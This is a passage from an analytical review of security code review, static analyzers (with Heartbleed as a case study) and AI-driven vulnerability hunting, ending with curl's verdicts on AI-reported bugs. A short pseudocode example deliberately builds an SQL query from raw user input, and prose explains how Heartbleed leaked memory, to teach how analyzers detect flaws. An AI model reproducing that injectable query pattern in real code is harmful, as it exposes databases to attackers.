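Participants who reviewed code more often did better in 2021, as did those who thought about vulnerabilities when writing their own programs. Thinking about vulnerabilities while programming also helped with the log flaw in 2022. This habit seems to matter more than seniority, and it works much like a prompt that reviewers give themselves.

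### How many readers it takes

If one reader is likely to miss a flaw, a project can ask several to review the code. If each reader independently has the same chance p of finding the flaw, the chance that all n readers miss it is (1 − p)ⁿ, and the chance that at least one finds it is 1 − (1 − p)ⁿ.

A prompted reader had a 19 in 41 chance of finding the log flaw. At least one of three such readers would find it about 85 percent of the time, and at least one of four about 92 percent. An unprompted reader had a 1 in 33 chance, so reaching 90 percent would take 75 readers. The table gives the number of readers needed for a 90 percent chance of finding each flaw.

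| Flaw | Prompted? | Chance for one reader | Readers needed |
|---|---|---|---|
| SQL injection | No | 52 in 80 | 3 |
| Unchecked quantity | No | 14 in 66 | 10 |
| MD5 | No | 7 in 33 | 10 |
| MD5 | Yes | 25 in 41 | 3 |
| Log flaw | No | 1 in 33 | 75 |
| Log flaw | Yes | 19 in 41 | 4 |

The figure of 75 is only a rough guide, because one success among 33 people is statistically compatible with a true success rate as high as about 16 percent, in which case 14 readers would be enough. Still, few projects could find even 10 readers for every change. Asking three or four people to look for security flaws would take much less effort, provided the instruction keeps working. The participants received it only once, and reviewers who see it above every change might soon stop noticing it.

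More seriously, reviewers on the same project are not independent. The formula would hold if a project drew its reviewers at random from the experiment's participants, but they are colleagues who have often learned from each other and work under the same rules. If none of them knows that MD5 is weak, a fourth reviewer will miss the flaw for the same reason as the first three.

Suppose, for example, that in half of all projects nobody knows that logs can leak private details, while in the other half each reader finds such a flaw 93 percent of the time. Averaged over all projects, a reader has about a 46 percent chance of finding the flaw, as in the experiment. But four readers from the same project will find it only about half the time, and so will 40, because adding readers doesn't help in projects where nobody knows about the problem.

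Reviewers can also all miss the same flaw because each relies on someone else to catch it. One participant who missed the MD5 flaw had assumed that there would be a separate security assessment. When several people review a change, each has more reason to assume that another has checked the difficult part.

It is unclear from the records of real projects whether extra reviewers help. Di Biase and his colleagues found that more than two reviewers took part in 39 of the 71 Chromium reviews that caught a flaw, and they tentatively recommended involving more people. But they did not report how many reviewers took part when a flaw was missed, so their figure can't show whether larger groups catch more. Paul and his colleagues compared reviews that caught flaws with reviews that missed them in Chromium OS, and found that the number of reviewers had no significant effect. Risky or complicated changes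 may attract more reviewers, which could hide a real benefit. A project that adds reviewers would probably gain most by choosing people with different knowledge. In three of the 71 Chromium cases, a reviewer called in a security expert, who then found the flaw.

### Reviewing code written by AI

Many of the changes that developers now review contain code from an AI assistant. *Securing AI-Generated Code* (2026) cites a study of 7,703 public-project files that developers had credited to AI tools. The study found at least one detectable weakness in 12.1 percent of the files, with the highest rates in Python code. The same paper cites research by Ji and colleagues, who found that developers trust such code too much, skip critical review and rate it as more secure than code written by people. *The Effect of Security-Focused Prompts on Reported Findings* (2026) describes an earlier experiment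 in which participants with an AI assistant wrote less secure code but were more likely to believe it was secure.

The people in that experiment were judging code they had just produced with the assistant's help. A reviewer who comes to the code later may be more detached. *Same Scrutiny, More Time* (2026) reports an experiment in which professional developers reviewed four Python files while a device tracked their eyes. Each file was about 77 lines long and contained deliberate faults. Some participants saw certain passages labelled as the work of an AI model, while others saw the same passages unlabelled. The label led reviewers to spend more time but did not change how they examined the code.

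This is no sign that reviewers skip code once they know it came from an AI model. But eye tracking measures attention, and participants in the vacation experiment had paid attention to the price formula without seeing what was wrong with it. Reviewers who know from a label where code came from still have to decide what to look for, whereas the instruction in the 2022 experiment named the kind of problem. Labels also don't help if developers submit an assistant's code as their own.

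Language models respond to a security prompt in a similar way. For *Broken by Default*, a 2026 study of AI-generated code, researchers collected 89 pieces of code that models had written and a mathematical tool had proved vulnerable. When asked to review their own code for security, the models identified 70 of the 89 pieces (79 percent) as vulnerable. This result isn't comparable with the lower figures for prompted people in the 2022 experiment, because the flaws were different and the models' test included only vulnerable code. A model that called everything vulnerable would have scored 100 percent.

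### Flaws that somebody has disguised

All these experiments used undisguised flaws. Braz and her colleagues based theirs on examples from the Common Weakness Enumeration (CWE), a public catalogue of types of software weakness. They made sure a reviewer could find each flaw from the changed code alone, and had professionals check that the code looked realistic and had no other problems.

An attacker would disguise the flaw. The Minnesota researchers' patches, for example, depended on code outside the diff, and contest entrants wrote comments to reassure the reader. An attacker can also choose the type of flaw. The share of unprompted reviewers who noticed each of the four undisguised flaws in these experiments ranged from 3 to 65 percent, so someone who wanted to get past review would avoid the SQL injection. The detection rates, especially those for prompted reviewers, therefore probably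 overstate how many reviewers would find a planted flaw.

The unprompted rates may not much overstate how often reviewers catch disguised flaws, because some are already so low. If 32 out of 33 people miss an undisguised flaw, disguise can hardly lower the rate further. The vacation formula needed no disguise, since its flaw was an omission. Disguise can even help the reviewer, because it often requires code that looks odd or has no clear purpose. Wheeler thought this was true of most of the contest entries that escaped his simple tools.

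To measure the effect of disguise, researchers would have to give reviewers the same flaw in plain and disguised versions, with and without a security instruction. The closest evidence so far comes from the contest judges, who could still miss a disguised flaw even though they were in much the same position as the participants who received a warning in 2021.

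## Heartbleed and the limits of static analyzers

Many participants in the Zurich experiments overlooked the vacation flaw, which was a missing check. Heartbleed was a far more serious mistake of the same kind in OpenSSL, a free library that many websites use to encrypt their connections. A reviewer approved the code, it remained in published versions for two years, and the leading static analyzers did not report the flaw. After the OpenSSL project disclosed Heartbleed on 7 April 2014, the makers of several analyzers explained why their tools had missed it.

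### The missing length check

OpenSSL lets either end of a connection send a "heartbeat", a short message to check that the other end is still responding. The message contains some data and a number giving the data's length, and the recipient replies with the same data. OpenSSL used that number to decide how many bytes to copy into the reply, without checking that the message contained that many. If the number was too large, the reply included whatever followed the message in memory, up to about 64 kilobytes.

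*The Matter of Heartbleed* (Durumeric, Kasten and colleagues, 2014) explains that that memory could contain passwords and the private keys behind a site's encryption. The paper estimates that 24 to 55 percent of popular sites with encrypted connections were vulnerable at first. The fix took only a few lines of code, which discard any heartbeat whose stated length is too large.

Robin Seggelmann, who wrote the feature, denied rumours that he had planted a backdoor, according to the Los Angeles Times' *German engineer who created ‘Heartbleed’ bug says it was an accident* (2014). He said he had forgotten to validate a length and the reviewer had also missed the omission. The Register (2014) suggested that Seggelmann and the reviewer, Stephen Henson, might have been the only two people to study the code before other software makers adopted it.

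The faulty code is orderly. *Dealing with Code That Is Opaque to Static Analysis* (Miller, Kupsch and colleagues, 2016) goes through it. The program reads the stated length, reserves enough memory for a reply of that length, and copies that many bytes. The actual size of the incoming record appears a few lines earlier, where the program passes it to another function. A reviewer could see both lengths, but to catch the bug had to notice that no line compared them.

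Testing also failed to expose the omission. In *How to Prevent the next Heartbleed*, Wheeler (2014) points out that most test suites mainly check what a program does with correct input, and OpenSSL answered correct heartbeats correctly. Some projects measure which lines their tests have run, but this cannot reveal that a line is missing. Fuzz testing produces incorrect input, but fuzz testers mostly looked for crashes, and a program that reads too much memory usually keeps running.

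Neel Mehta of Google found the flaw on 21 March 2014 while reviewing source code. The Finnish company Codenomicon found it independently twelve days later with an extended fuzz tester. In 2015, according to Wheeler, Hanno Böck combined a newer fuzz tester with a memory checker and found Heartbleed automatically in six hours.

### How analyzers look for flaws

The simplest analyzers use pattern rules. Flawfinder, for example, compares a program's text with a list of risky C functions, as *An Empirical Study of Rule-Based and Learning-Based Approaches* (2021) describes. A rule that reported every use of memcpy, the C function for copying memory, would have reported the faulty line in OpenSSL, but also every harmless copy. In *A New Development for Coverity and Heartbleed*, the computer scientist John Regehr observes that anyone can write an analyzer that flags Heartbleed by having it flag every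 line. The hard part is flagging Heartbleed without producing so many useless warnings that people overlook it.

Taint analysis narrows the search by considering where data comes from. *Heartbleed and static analysis* (Lippert, 2014) explains it in terms of sources and sinks. A source is a place where untrusted data enters the program, such as a network connection. A sink is an operation that such data could make dangerous, such as a memory copy whose length an outsider can choose.

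The analyzer marks data from a source as tainted, then follows it through the program. If the program copies a tainted value or uses it in a calculation, the result is also tainted. The analyzer removes the mark if the value passes through a sanitizer, a step that makes it safe. If a tainted value reaches a sink, the analyzer reports a possible flaw.

Deeper analyses also track which values a variable can have. In an earlier post on Heartbleed, Regehr describes how Frama-C, an analyzer for C, would have handled the copy. The stated length occupies two bytes, so Frama-C would have recorded its range as 0 to 65,535. Frama-C also checks that a copy does not extend past the end of either the original data or the destination. The destination was large enough, but the original data could be much shorter than 65,535 bytes, so Frama-C would have flagged the copy.

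With the missing check added, the program reaches the copy only if the stated length fits the message, so an analyzer that takes the check into account can rule out larger lengths.

This precision takes a lot of computation because each independent yes-or-no decision doubles the number of paths a program can take. Thirty such decisions produce more than a billion paths (2³⁰). To finish in a reasonable time, an analyzer must merge some paths or skip some. Merging can produce a warning about a combination of values that never occurs, and skipping can hide a real flaw.

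### One query in three versions

The three versions of a program below show what a taint rule can and cannot determine. Each looks up an employee by a number that a user has typed, as in the SQL injection experiment, and they differ only in how they prepare that number.

```
Version 1:  number = user_input()
Version 2:  number = to_integer(user_input())
Version 3:  number = remove_quotes(user_input())

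Then:       run_query("SELECT name FROM staff WHERE id = " + number)
```

The rule treats `user_input` as a source and `run_query` as a sink. In version 1, the input goes straight into the database command, so the analyzer reports a flaw. The report is correct because the user could type part of a command instead of a number.

In version 2, the program converts the input to a whole number and stops if it can't, so only a number can reach the database. If the rule lists `to_integer` as a sanitizer, the analyzer removes the taint and correctly reports nothing. Otherwise, it reports a false positive.

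Version 3 removes quotation marks from the input, but the code is still vulnerable. Removing them can help when a command encloses the user's text in quotation marks, because it stops the user from closing them early. Here, the command has no quotation marks around the number.

The analyzer's result for version 3 depends on how the rule classifies `remove_quotes`. If the rule lists the function as a sanitizer, the analyzer misses the flaw. If it doesn't, the analyzer treats the function's output as tainted and reports the flaw, but the same policy would also make it warn about any home-made cleaning function that works perfectly.

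An ordinary taint rule records only that input was cleaned. To check whether it was cleaned enough, an analyzer would have to determine which characters can remain and what they mean at that point in the command. A reviewer can make the same mistake by trusting a function because of its reassuring name.

### Why Heartbleed drew no warning

In principle, Heartbleed resembles version 1, because a number from an outsider controls a memory copy without passing through a sanitizer. Coverity, a commercial analyzer, had examined OpenSSL through a free service for open-source projects. It reported 151 defects but not Heartbleed, as Regehr noted after going through some of them with his students.

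Coverity's makers first tried other settings, without success, and then examined how the data moved through the program, as they describe in a post now published as Black Duck's *detecting heartbleed with static analysis*. The analyzer tried to follow untrusted data from the library call where it entered, but OpenSSL stored the data inside several layers of structures. The engineers struggled to understand the route even by hand. A code comment described a field as a pointer to the record's data, but the analyzer made little use of comments.

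GrammaTech ran into similar trouble with its competing analyzer, CodeSonar. According to GrammaTech's *Finding Heartbleed with CodeSonar*, OpenSSL used indirect calls both to read from the network and to reserve memory. In an indirect call, the program looks up which function to call as it runs, so an analyzer has to work out the possible destinations. CodeSonar did this correctly, but its developers had overlooked a few subtle ways taint can spread. Its default settings also favoured speed over thoroughness, so it did not explore enough of the program.

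After correcting these problems, GrammaTech detected Heartbleed in a selected part of OpenSSL, and then in the whole library. It was still looking for settings that would detect the flaw reliably and at a reasonable speed. Wheeler gives little credit for detection in a selected part, since someone who already knows where the flaw is doesn't need a tool to find it.

One free analyzer, CQual++, may have been able to find Heartbleed before it was disclosed. Wheeler cites an anonymous government laboratory employee who reported that CQual++ found the flaw when the commercial tools he tried did not, though he called it a bit difficult to run and interpret. The report is second-hand and dates from after the disclosure, so it is weak evidence that anyone would have found the flaw this way.

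### Coverity's new rule

Coverity's engineers then noticed that OpenSSL swapped the two bytes of the stated length. Network protocols usually send the most significant byte of a number first, but most PCs and servers store the least significant byte first, so programs on these machines have to swap the bytes of numbers they receive. Programs have few other reasons to do this, so a byte swap suggests that a number came from outside the program.

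The new rule treated the result of a byte swap as tainted, so the analyzer could start tracking the data a few lines before the faulty copy instead of following it from the network. With this rule, Coverity reported Heartbleed. Trail of Bits' *Using Static Analysis and Clang To Find Heartbleed* (2014) describes a checker that uses the same idea in another analyzer.

The main risk was more false positives, since image and encryption software sometimes swaps bytes in trusted data. To limit them, Coverity made the rule flag code only when it combined the swapped bytes into a larger number and then used that number in a sink, such as the length of a copy. The rule flagged only a handful of other places in OpenSSL, and the engineers wrote that they believed, or at least hoped, that these were false alarms. They planned to test the rule on more than 60 million lines of open-source code before releasing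 it. According to a note later added to the post, the product now detects Heartbleed, but the post does not give a false positive rate.

The rule can also miss the same mistake elsewhere. GrammaTech called the approach fragile because programmers can write a byte swap in a dozen or more ways, and some machines and data formats need no swap. Regehr also raised the problem of when to remove the taint. A program might check a number against an upper limit but not a lower one, or against a limit that is far too high. If the analyzer accepts any comparison as a sanitizer, it will miss flaws for the same reason as in version 3 of the query.

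Finding a known flaw with a rule written for it is little evidence of how many unknown flaws the rule will find. Still, the rule was useful for finding other instances of the same mistake, including any in OpenSSL.

### What no analyzer can decide

Better engineering could have caught Heartbleed, but some misses are unavoidable for mathematical reasons. In 1936, Alan Turing proved that no program can tell, for every program, whether it will finish or run forever. Rice's theorem, published by Henry Gordon Rice in 1953, extends this to any behaviour that some programs have and others don't, so no program can always tell which ones have it.

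No analyzer can always tell whether a program ever copies too much memory. Suppose one could. If we add a faulty copy after the last step of a program that never copies too much memory, the new program makes that copy only if the original finishes. The analyzer could therefore determine whether the original finishes, which Turing proved no algorithm can do for every program.

An analyzer can still give the right answer for many programs, but for others it must give a wrong answer, give no answer or keep running. The theorem doesn't explain why a tool missed a particular flaw. Regehr writes that the usual obstacles in practice are indirection and decisions that depend on data, as in OpenSSL.

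The designers can, however, choose which errors to accept. Frama-C flags every operation it cannot prove safe, so within its assumptions it misses no flaw of the kinds it covers. Someone then has to deal with every warning, including those about safe code. Regehr did not expect anyone to get OpenSSL through Frama-C in "a week or three". A company founded by Frama-C developers had used it on PolarSSL, a rival encryption library, and promised that the resulting version was free of 15 types of flaw listed in the CWE catalogue.

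### Fewer alarms, more misses

Most commercial analyzers instead try to find many flaws with little help from the user. Reporting fewer possible flaws reduces false positives but also hides some real flaws. Suppose a program has 10,000 functions, of which 10 are vulnerable. A cautious setting finds five of them and wrongly flags 1 percent of the safe functions, or about 100. A more sensitive setting finds eight but wrongly flags 10 percent, or about 1,000. Finding the three additional flaws therefore adds about 900 false alarms.

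The sensitive setting may still be right for code that protects a bank or an encryption key. A commenter on Regehr's post who had worked on PREfix, another analyzer, recalled that 99 percent of the reports from its first taint analysis were false, but one of the real flaws it found was in a system-level encryption module.

Miller and colleagues write that tools fail to report some flaws partly because they suppress uncertain results. They also note that tools have no way to indicate a confidence level when they report nothing, so a user who sees no warning can't tell whether the analyzer showed that the code was safe or stopped because it could no longer track the data. They propose measuring how difficult each part of a program is to analyze, so that developers could simplify the worst parts. They acknowledge that vendors already have much of this information but have little commercial reason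 to publicize their tools' weaknesses.

### Libraries, intentions and incomplete code

An analyzer also depends on descriptions of the libraries a program uses. The query example works only because the rule identifies `user_input` as a source and `run_query` as a sink. If a company writes its own function for sending commands to the database, the analyzer needs either that function's source code or a description of what it does, called a model. Without either, it may fail to flag version 1.

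Regehr ran into this problem with OpenSSL, which managed some of its memory through its own functions instead of the standard ones. When he replaced these with the standard functions and ran Coverity again, it still missed Heartbleed but reported 173 new defects, mostly failures to release memory and uses of memory after its release. Some of these may have been side effects of his changes, but the number suggests how much an analyzer can overlook when it has no model of such functions.

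Other flaws violate an intention that appears nowhere in the code. For example, the vacation program paid employees for requesting a negative number of days. An analyzer can determine that the number may be negative, but negative numbers are normal in programs that handle temperatures or refunds. So someone would have to write a rule that this number must be positive, and a developer who thought of that would probably have written the check as well.

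Earlier research suggests such gaps are common. *An Empirical Study of False Negatives and Positives of Static Code Analyzers* (2024) cites several studies in which analyzers missed most real defects because no rule covered them or they were specific to the program's field.

Finally, the analyzer may be unable to process the code. Some tools observe the program as it compiles, so they need every library and definition it requires. A single file or short example may not compile, and old code often stops compiling as its libraries change. *Fixed Detectors, Moving Code* (Tang, Zhang and Cai, 2026) cites a study of 100 Java projects in which only 38 percent of the recorded history could still be compiled. Tools that read source files directly avoid this problem but have less information. Given only a fragment, they may find the database command but not where the number came from.

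### Tests on real vulnerabilities

Researchers can measure the combined effect of these problems by running analyzers on code with known vulnerabilities. *An Empirical Study on the Effectiveness of Static C Code Analyzers* (Lipp, Banescu and Pretschner, 2022) tested five free analyzers and one commercial one on 192 vulnerabilities from 27 real C projects. The analyzers missed between 47 and 80 percent of the vulnerabilities.

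Combining the analyzers reduced the share of flaws they missed to between 30 and 69 percent, because different tools found different ones. But it also increased the share of functions with a warning by 15 percentage points. In a program with 10,000 functions, developers would have another 1,500 to check.

Results for Java were similar. Li and colleagues (2023) ran seven free analyzers on 165 real vulnerabilities. Even together, the analyzers missed 117, or 70.9 percent. Both Li's and Tang's teams contrasted their results with analyzers' good performance on artificial examples, which tend to be short and self-contained, so an analyzer has less opportunity to lose track of the data.

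In *An Empirical Study of Static Analysis Tools for Secure Code Review*, Charoenwet and colleagues (2024) checked whether analyzers would have warned about the functions that became vulnerable in 815 commits, which had contributed to 319 vulnerabilities in 92 C and C++ projects. A single tool warned about these functions in 52 percent of the commits, but at least 76 percent of the warnings in vulnerable functions were unrelated to the vulnerability. The tools missed 22 percent of the commits because of limitations in their rules.

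An irrelevant warning can still help if it leads a reviewer to the right function. When Charoenwet and his colleagues ranked functions by their warnings, a reviewer would have had to read 13 percent less harmless code before reaching the first vulnerable function. This modest benefit assumes that the reviewer then recognizes the flaw without a warning that identifies it.

### Warnings that remain after the repair

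Tang and his co-authors tested whether analyzers could tell vulnerable code from repaired code. They used 20,000 versions of C and C++ programs from 1,116 projects, dating from 2016 to 2025. Half the versions contained a known vulnerability, and the other half were versions from immediately after a repair.

The researchers tested three releases each of CodeQL, which lets users search a program as if it were a database, and Infer, which analyzes a program function by function. They also tested Semgrep, which mainly looks for structural patterns. They counted a version as flagged if the tool gave at least one relevant warning in the files the repair changed.

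| Analyzer | Vulnerable versions flagged | Repaired versions flagged |
|---|---|---|
| CodeQL, 2021 | 7.1% | 7.5% |
| CodeQL, 2024 | 13.1% | 13.0% |
| CodeQL, 2026 | 20.7% | 21.3% |
| Infer, 2021 | 3.6% | 3.7% |
| Infer, 2024 | 10.2% | 5.1% |
| Infer, 2026 | 8.5% | 8.9% |
| Semgrep | 46.5% | 47.9% |

CodeQL's warnings about vulnerable versions almost tripled between 2021 and 2026, but its warnings about repaired versions increased by nearly the same factor, so the first increase alone doesn't show that CodeQL improved. Only the 2024 release of Infer flagged vulnerable code clearly more often than repaired code, and the 2026 release no longer did.

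The test is hard to pass because the two versions of a program are usually almost identical. A warning about some other part of the file will appear both before and after the repair. In one version of HAProxy, a program that distributes network traffic, CodeQL flagged a comparison unrelated to the vulnerability. The repair didn't change that line, so the warning remained.

For the same reason, the figures in the last column are not ordinary false positive rates. A repaired file can contain other real flaws, and a warning about one of them is correct. But the figures do show that a warning somewhere in a vulnerable file is poor evidence that the tool has found the vulnerability, so studies that count any such warning as a success overstate what analyzers detect.

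Tang and his colleagues also examined cases in which a tool's score had fallen sharply within a project. Only 6 of 39 CodeQL warnings and 2 of 620 Infer warnings in these cases were on a line that the repair had changed. Counting only those warnings as correct can be too strict. A correct warning about Heartbleed would have been on the memory copy, but the repair added a check before it. The researchers chose these cases because they were extreme, so the proportions may not be typical.

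The experiment also showed that analyses often failed while appearing to succeed. Semgrep reported success on every run, but in 79 percent of cases its records contained errors in reading the code or rules that timed out. Infer recorded thousands of runs as successful even though it had captured no code or failed to capture it properly. A project that checks only for warnings would treat such results as clean.

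The evidence for most analyzers is weaker than for these three. *Many Tools, Few Exploitable Vulnerabilities* (2026) reviewed research on 246 analyzers and found that the developers of only 11.8 percent claimed to have detected an exploitable vulnerability. Nearly all the developers tested their tools on their own benchmarks, which makes the results hard to compare. They also concentrated on the same well-known flaws, such as SQL injection, and paid less attention to insecure designs and risks from outside suppliers.

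The vulnerabilities in these benchmarks were mostly or entirely accidental. Miss rates are probably higher for planted flaws, because an attacker can test them against the same tools first. Language models may be able to judge some of the intentions that fixed rules don't cover, but they make errors of their own.

### What developers do with the warnings

A warning helps only if somebody reads and acts on it. Help Net Security's *91% noise* reports on a 2025 study by the company Ghost Security, which scanned nearly 3,000 public projects for three types of flaw. More than 91 percent of the warnings were false, and checking each one by hand took about 10 minutes on average. At that rate, 100 warnings take almost 17 hours to check and yield at most nine real flaws, or nearly two hours of work for each. Ghost Security has a commercial interest in showing that traditional analyzers perform badly,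 so its figure may be too high.

Developers respond to frequent false alarms by ignoring warnings, switching off rules or abandoning the tool. Wadhams (2024) reviewed research on why developers avoid or give up on security analyzers, including a study in which Johnson and colleagues interviewed 20 developers. The interviewees thought static analysis was worthwhile, but false positives and poorly presented warnings discouraged them from using it.

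In *Do Developers Use Static Application Security Testing (SAST) Tools*, Bennett, Hall and colleagues (2024) asked 1,003 developers whether they used security analyzers, and only 204 did. Of those, 59 percent used only one tool, and 54 percent had not configured the tool for their project. They want to help developers combine and configure tools, because this would probably detect many more vulnerabilities. Configuration seems the better place to start, because describing a project's sources, sinks and sanitizers can remove false alarms as well as reveal missed flaws, whereas each additional tool produces more warnings to check.

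## Automated systems that hunt for flaws, 2025–2026

An automated system can check some of its warnings by running the program on different inputs to find one that makes the program fail. In August 2025, DARPA, the US military's research agency, announced the results of the AI Cyber Challenge, a two-year competition for systems that find and repair flaws without human help. The organizers had planted flaws in real open-source projects so they could count how many the systems missed.

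Forty-two teams entered and seven reached the final, which *SoK* (Zhang, Park and colleagues, 2026) analyzes. The systems ran unattended for about 143 hours. Each team could spend up to $85,000 on cloud computing and $50,000 on language models. According to *ATLANTIS* (2025), the winning team's paper, the systems had no internet access except to approved models and whatever they needed to build the software.

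The projects, which included xz, ranged from 16,000 to 4.9 million lines of code. For 33 of the 63 planted flaws, the systems had to search a whole project. The other 30 were in proposed changes, so the systems could start from a diff, as a human reviewer does.

### How the systems combined their methods

Every team used fuzz testing. A fuzz tester generates inputs, and a small program called a harness passes each one to the code under test. The fuzz tester keeps the inputs that reach new parts of the code and varies them further, while a memory checker or similar tool stops the program when it performs a forbidden operation. Fuzz testing works poorly when the code accepts only complicated inputs, because random changes to a PDF file, for example, mostly produce files that the program rejects at once.

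Six of the seven teams used language models to get past this obstacle. The model read the code that processes the input, worked out the expected format, and wrote a short script to generate suitable inputs. In some systems, it also wrote inputs to satisfy conditions that the fuzz tester had failed to meet.

Most teams also had models look for flaws directly. Static analyzers and lists of risky functions helped identify suspicious places, and a model discarded the unlikely ones. Another model then tried to construct an input that would trigger the suspected flaw. It could run the program, see how far the input got, and try again. Five systems gave their fuzz testers the results, including failed attempts, because a small change to a near miss might trigger the flaw.

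Teams balanced AI and non-AI techniques differently. Theori, which placed third, told reporters that its system would still work without the non-AI part, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *#DEFCON*.

An input that triggers the flaw is a proof of vulnerability, which anyone can check by running the program on that input. Once a system had a proof, a model wrote a patch. The system then rebuilt the program, confirmed that the input no longer caused a failure, and usually ran the project's tests.

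### What they found and what it cost

DARPA's *AI Cyber Challenge marks pivotal inflection point for cyber defense* (2025) reports that the seven systems together found 54 of the 63 planted flaws (86 percent) and patched 43. The announcement says they patched 68 percent of the flaws identified, but 43 is 68 percent of all 63 flaws and 80 percent of the 54 found. These totals count a flaw if any of the seven systems found it, so a single system would probably do worse.

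The systems also found 18 flaws that nobody had planted, and the teams supplied 11 patches for them. Zhang and his colleagues later counted 25 such flaws. The finalists continued this work on real software after the competition and had found 83 vulnerabilities by March 2026, according to Cybersecurity Dive.

DARPA put the average cost at about $152 per task. This is not the cost of finding one flaw, because according to DARPA's *AIxCC Main Stage Presentation*, a successful task could be a proof, a patch, a verdict on somebody else's warning, or a bundle of related results. The teams spent $359,000 in total, or about $5,000 for each of the 72 planted and unplanned flaws in DARPA's count. This figure is also rough, because the seven teams were often paying to find the same flaw.

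To see how much the language models contributed, Zhang and his colleagues ran ordinary fuzz testing on the same flaws. It found 30 of the 40 in C but only 4 of the 23 in Java, where inputs tend to have more complicated rules. The competing systems found 22 flaws that ordinary fuzz testing had missed, 15 of them in tasks that came with a diff. The researchers mostly credit the models, which could go straight from a change in the code to an input that exploited it. Some of these flaws involved indirect calls, which had made Heartbleed harder for static analyzers to find.

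Many failures had mundane causes. The Wireshark project needed about a terabyte of disk space, which probably explains why two of the leading systems stopped scoring partway through. One flaw caused a crash only when the program ran a second time, so systems that ran it once discarded valid proofs. Other failures were errors of reasoning. No system found either of two planted flaws in curl, a widely used program for transferring data, because they required several cryptographic steps in a row and the models' small errors accumulated.

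### Planted, but mostly not disguised

The organizers planted the flaws to test the systems, not to deceive a reviewer, and based most of them on past accidental flaws. A few imitated backdoors, but some of these contained the word "flag", a convention from hacking contests, and patching agents easily repaired these by deleting the labelled code.

An obfuscated backdoor in a Java project was among seven flaws that nobody patched in the competition or in the researchers' later tests. Zhang and his colleagues attribute the backdoor's survival to a crash that gave little indication of where the problem was, so the case doesn't show how much the obfuscation helped. The contest results are therefore better evidence about accidental flaws than about disguised ones. The systems' fuzz testing would have missed the xz backdoor, because ordinary builds of xz did not contain it.

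### Patches that passed the tests

An automatic check can also accept a bad repair. Zhang and his colleagues gave two patching agents a working proof of each planted flaw. Anthropic's Claude Code wrote patches that passed every automatic check for 53 of the 63 flaws, but experts who read the patches found that it had correctly repaired only 33. The other agent passed the checks for 57 flaws and correctly repaired 31.

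Some patches hid the symptom, for instance by limiting how many times a faulty loop could repeat. Others blocked the route the proof had used but left another open. When patching one Wireshark flaw, the agents confused the length given in a packet with the length the program had verified, a distinction OpenSSL's programmers had also missed in Heartbleed. The best competing systems did better, but 16 to 21 percent of their patches were still wrong.

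### Old flaws in heavily tested code

In April 2026, Anthropic announced Claude Mythos Preview, a language model that it made available only to selected organizations because of the model's hacking ability. *Assessing Claude Mythos Preview's cybersecurity capabilities* (Carlini, Cheng and colleagues, 2026) describes how the company used the model to look for unknown flaws. The model first ranked a project's files by how likely they were to contain interesting flaws. Many copies then worked in parallel, each starting from a different file and essentially told to find a vulnerability. They could read the code, run it and use a debugger. A final copy reviewed each report to filter out trivial problems.

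One of the flaws had been present for 27 years in OpenBSD, an operating system known for its security. It let an outsider crash a machine over the network. The code failed to check one end of a range of numbers, which was normally harmless. It could cause a crash only when combined with a second mistake, under a condition that looked impossible unless the reader considered how computers handle very large numbers. Reviewers who looked at either mistake alone had little reason to worry.

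Another was in FFmpeg, a library that many services use to process video. The mistake dated from 2003 but became exploitable only in 2010, when somebody reorganized the code, which makes it an accidental example of what the Minnesota researchers called an immature vulnerability. Anthropic says that automated tests had run the faulty line five million times without detecting the problem. The line goes wrong only if a video frame has far more parts than any normal video would use, so repeated tests without such a frame could not reveal the flaw.

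These discoveries took many attempts. A thousand runs on OpenBSD cost just under $20,000 and produced several dozen other findings. The run that found the 27-year-old flaw cost less than $50, but Carlini and his colleagues point out that nobody could have known in advance which run would succeed.

Most of the flaws they describe are memory errors, partly because these are easy to confirm. If a memory checker reports that a program wrote outside its reserved area, there is little doubt that the flaw is real. Anthropic had earlier sent Mozilla, the maker of the Firefox browser, 112 reports from an older model, and all proved correct. A memory checker doesn't detect when an input makes a program calculate the wrong price for a vacation.

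### From a model's claim to a maintainer's patch

Anthropic publishes a running count of what its models have found in open-source software, which makes it possible to separate claims from confirmed results. Anthropic (2026) gives these totals for 2 November 2026:

| Stage | Findings |
|---|---|
| Candidates produced by the models | 37,966 |
| Reviewed by outside security firms | 6,376 |
| Judged valid by those firms | 6,009 |
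| Reported to maintainers | 5,087 |
| Answered by maintainers | 3,635 |
| Patched by maintainers | 629 |

The firms judged 94 percent of the findings they reviewed to be valid. But they had reviewed only about one in six candidates, and Anthropic prioritizes the most serious ones, so the rate may not hold for the rest. According to Anthropic's *About this dashboard* (2026), valid findings include duplicates and bugs that maintainers do not intend to fix. Anthropic also sent 3,225 of the 5,087 reports directly to maintainers without outside review, and a maintainer's reply does not confirm that a reported bug is real.

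A patch is better evidence because a maintainer usually has to accept that something is wrong before changing the code. Patrick Garrity of the security company VulnCheck has criticized how few patches there are. In Infosecurity Magazine's *Anthropic's Glasswing Finds Many Security Flaws Yet Delivers Few Fixes* (2026), he counts 217 fixes, 1,654 duplicates and 419 withdrawn entries in Anthropic's public ledger. Anthropic itself counts 629 patches, which is still only 12 percent of the reports. The other 88 percent aren't necessarily false, since maintainers may not have had time to deal with them.

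Mozilla's results are more convincing because Mozilla maintains the code. The Next Web's *Mozilla patched 271 Firefox bugs found by Anthropic's Mythos* reports that Mozilla fixed 271 vulnerabilities identified by Mythos Preview in a single release, Firefox 150. Mozilla said that an elite human researcher could have found any of them. The number depends partly on how one counts. Tech Trenches' *Why AI Security Tools Still Need Your Engineers* reports that the official security notice grouped the 271 under 41 entries.

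### Six months of reports to curl

Daniel Stenberg, curl's lead developer, has published the most detailed account by a maintainer. His project already used static analyzers, strict compiler warnings and fuzz testing. In the eight to ten months before May 2026, several AI tools also led to 200 to 300 bug fixes, and probably a dozen or more of those bugs were vulnerabilities.

In *Mythos finds a curl vulnerability*, Stenberg (2026) describes a scan of curl's 178,000 lines that someone with access to Mythos Preview ran for him. The report listed five "confirmed" vulnerabilities. After several hours of work, curl's security team agreed with one, which it rated low severity. Three of the others were limitations that curl's documentation already described, and the fourth was an ordinary bug. Stenberg concluded that the publicity around the model had been mainly marketing, but he wrote that AI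 tools in general were much better at finding flaws than older analyzers.

In November, Anthropic's scanning service sent curl another 45 claimed vulnerabilities. Stenberg, in *curl on OSS-Scanner*, gives the maintainers' verdicts:

- 5 were vulnerabilities, all of low severity.
- 36 were ordinary bugs.
- 3 were not bugs.
- 1 had the problem backwards, and its proposed fix would have introduced the vulnerability it warned about.

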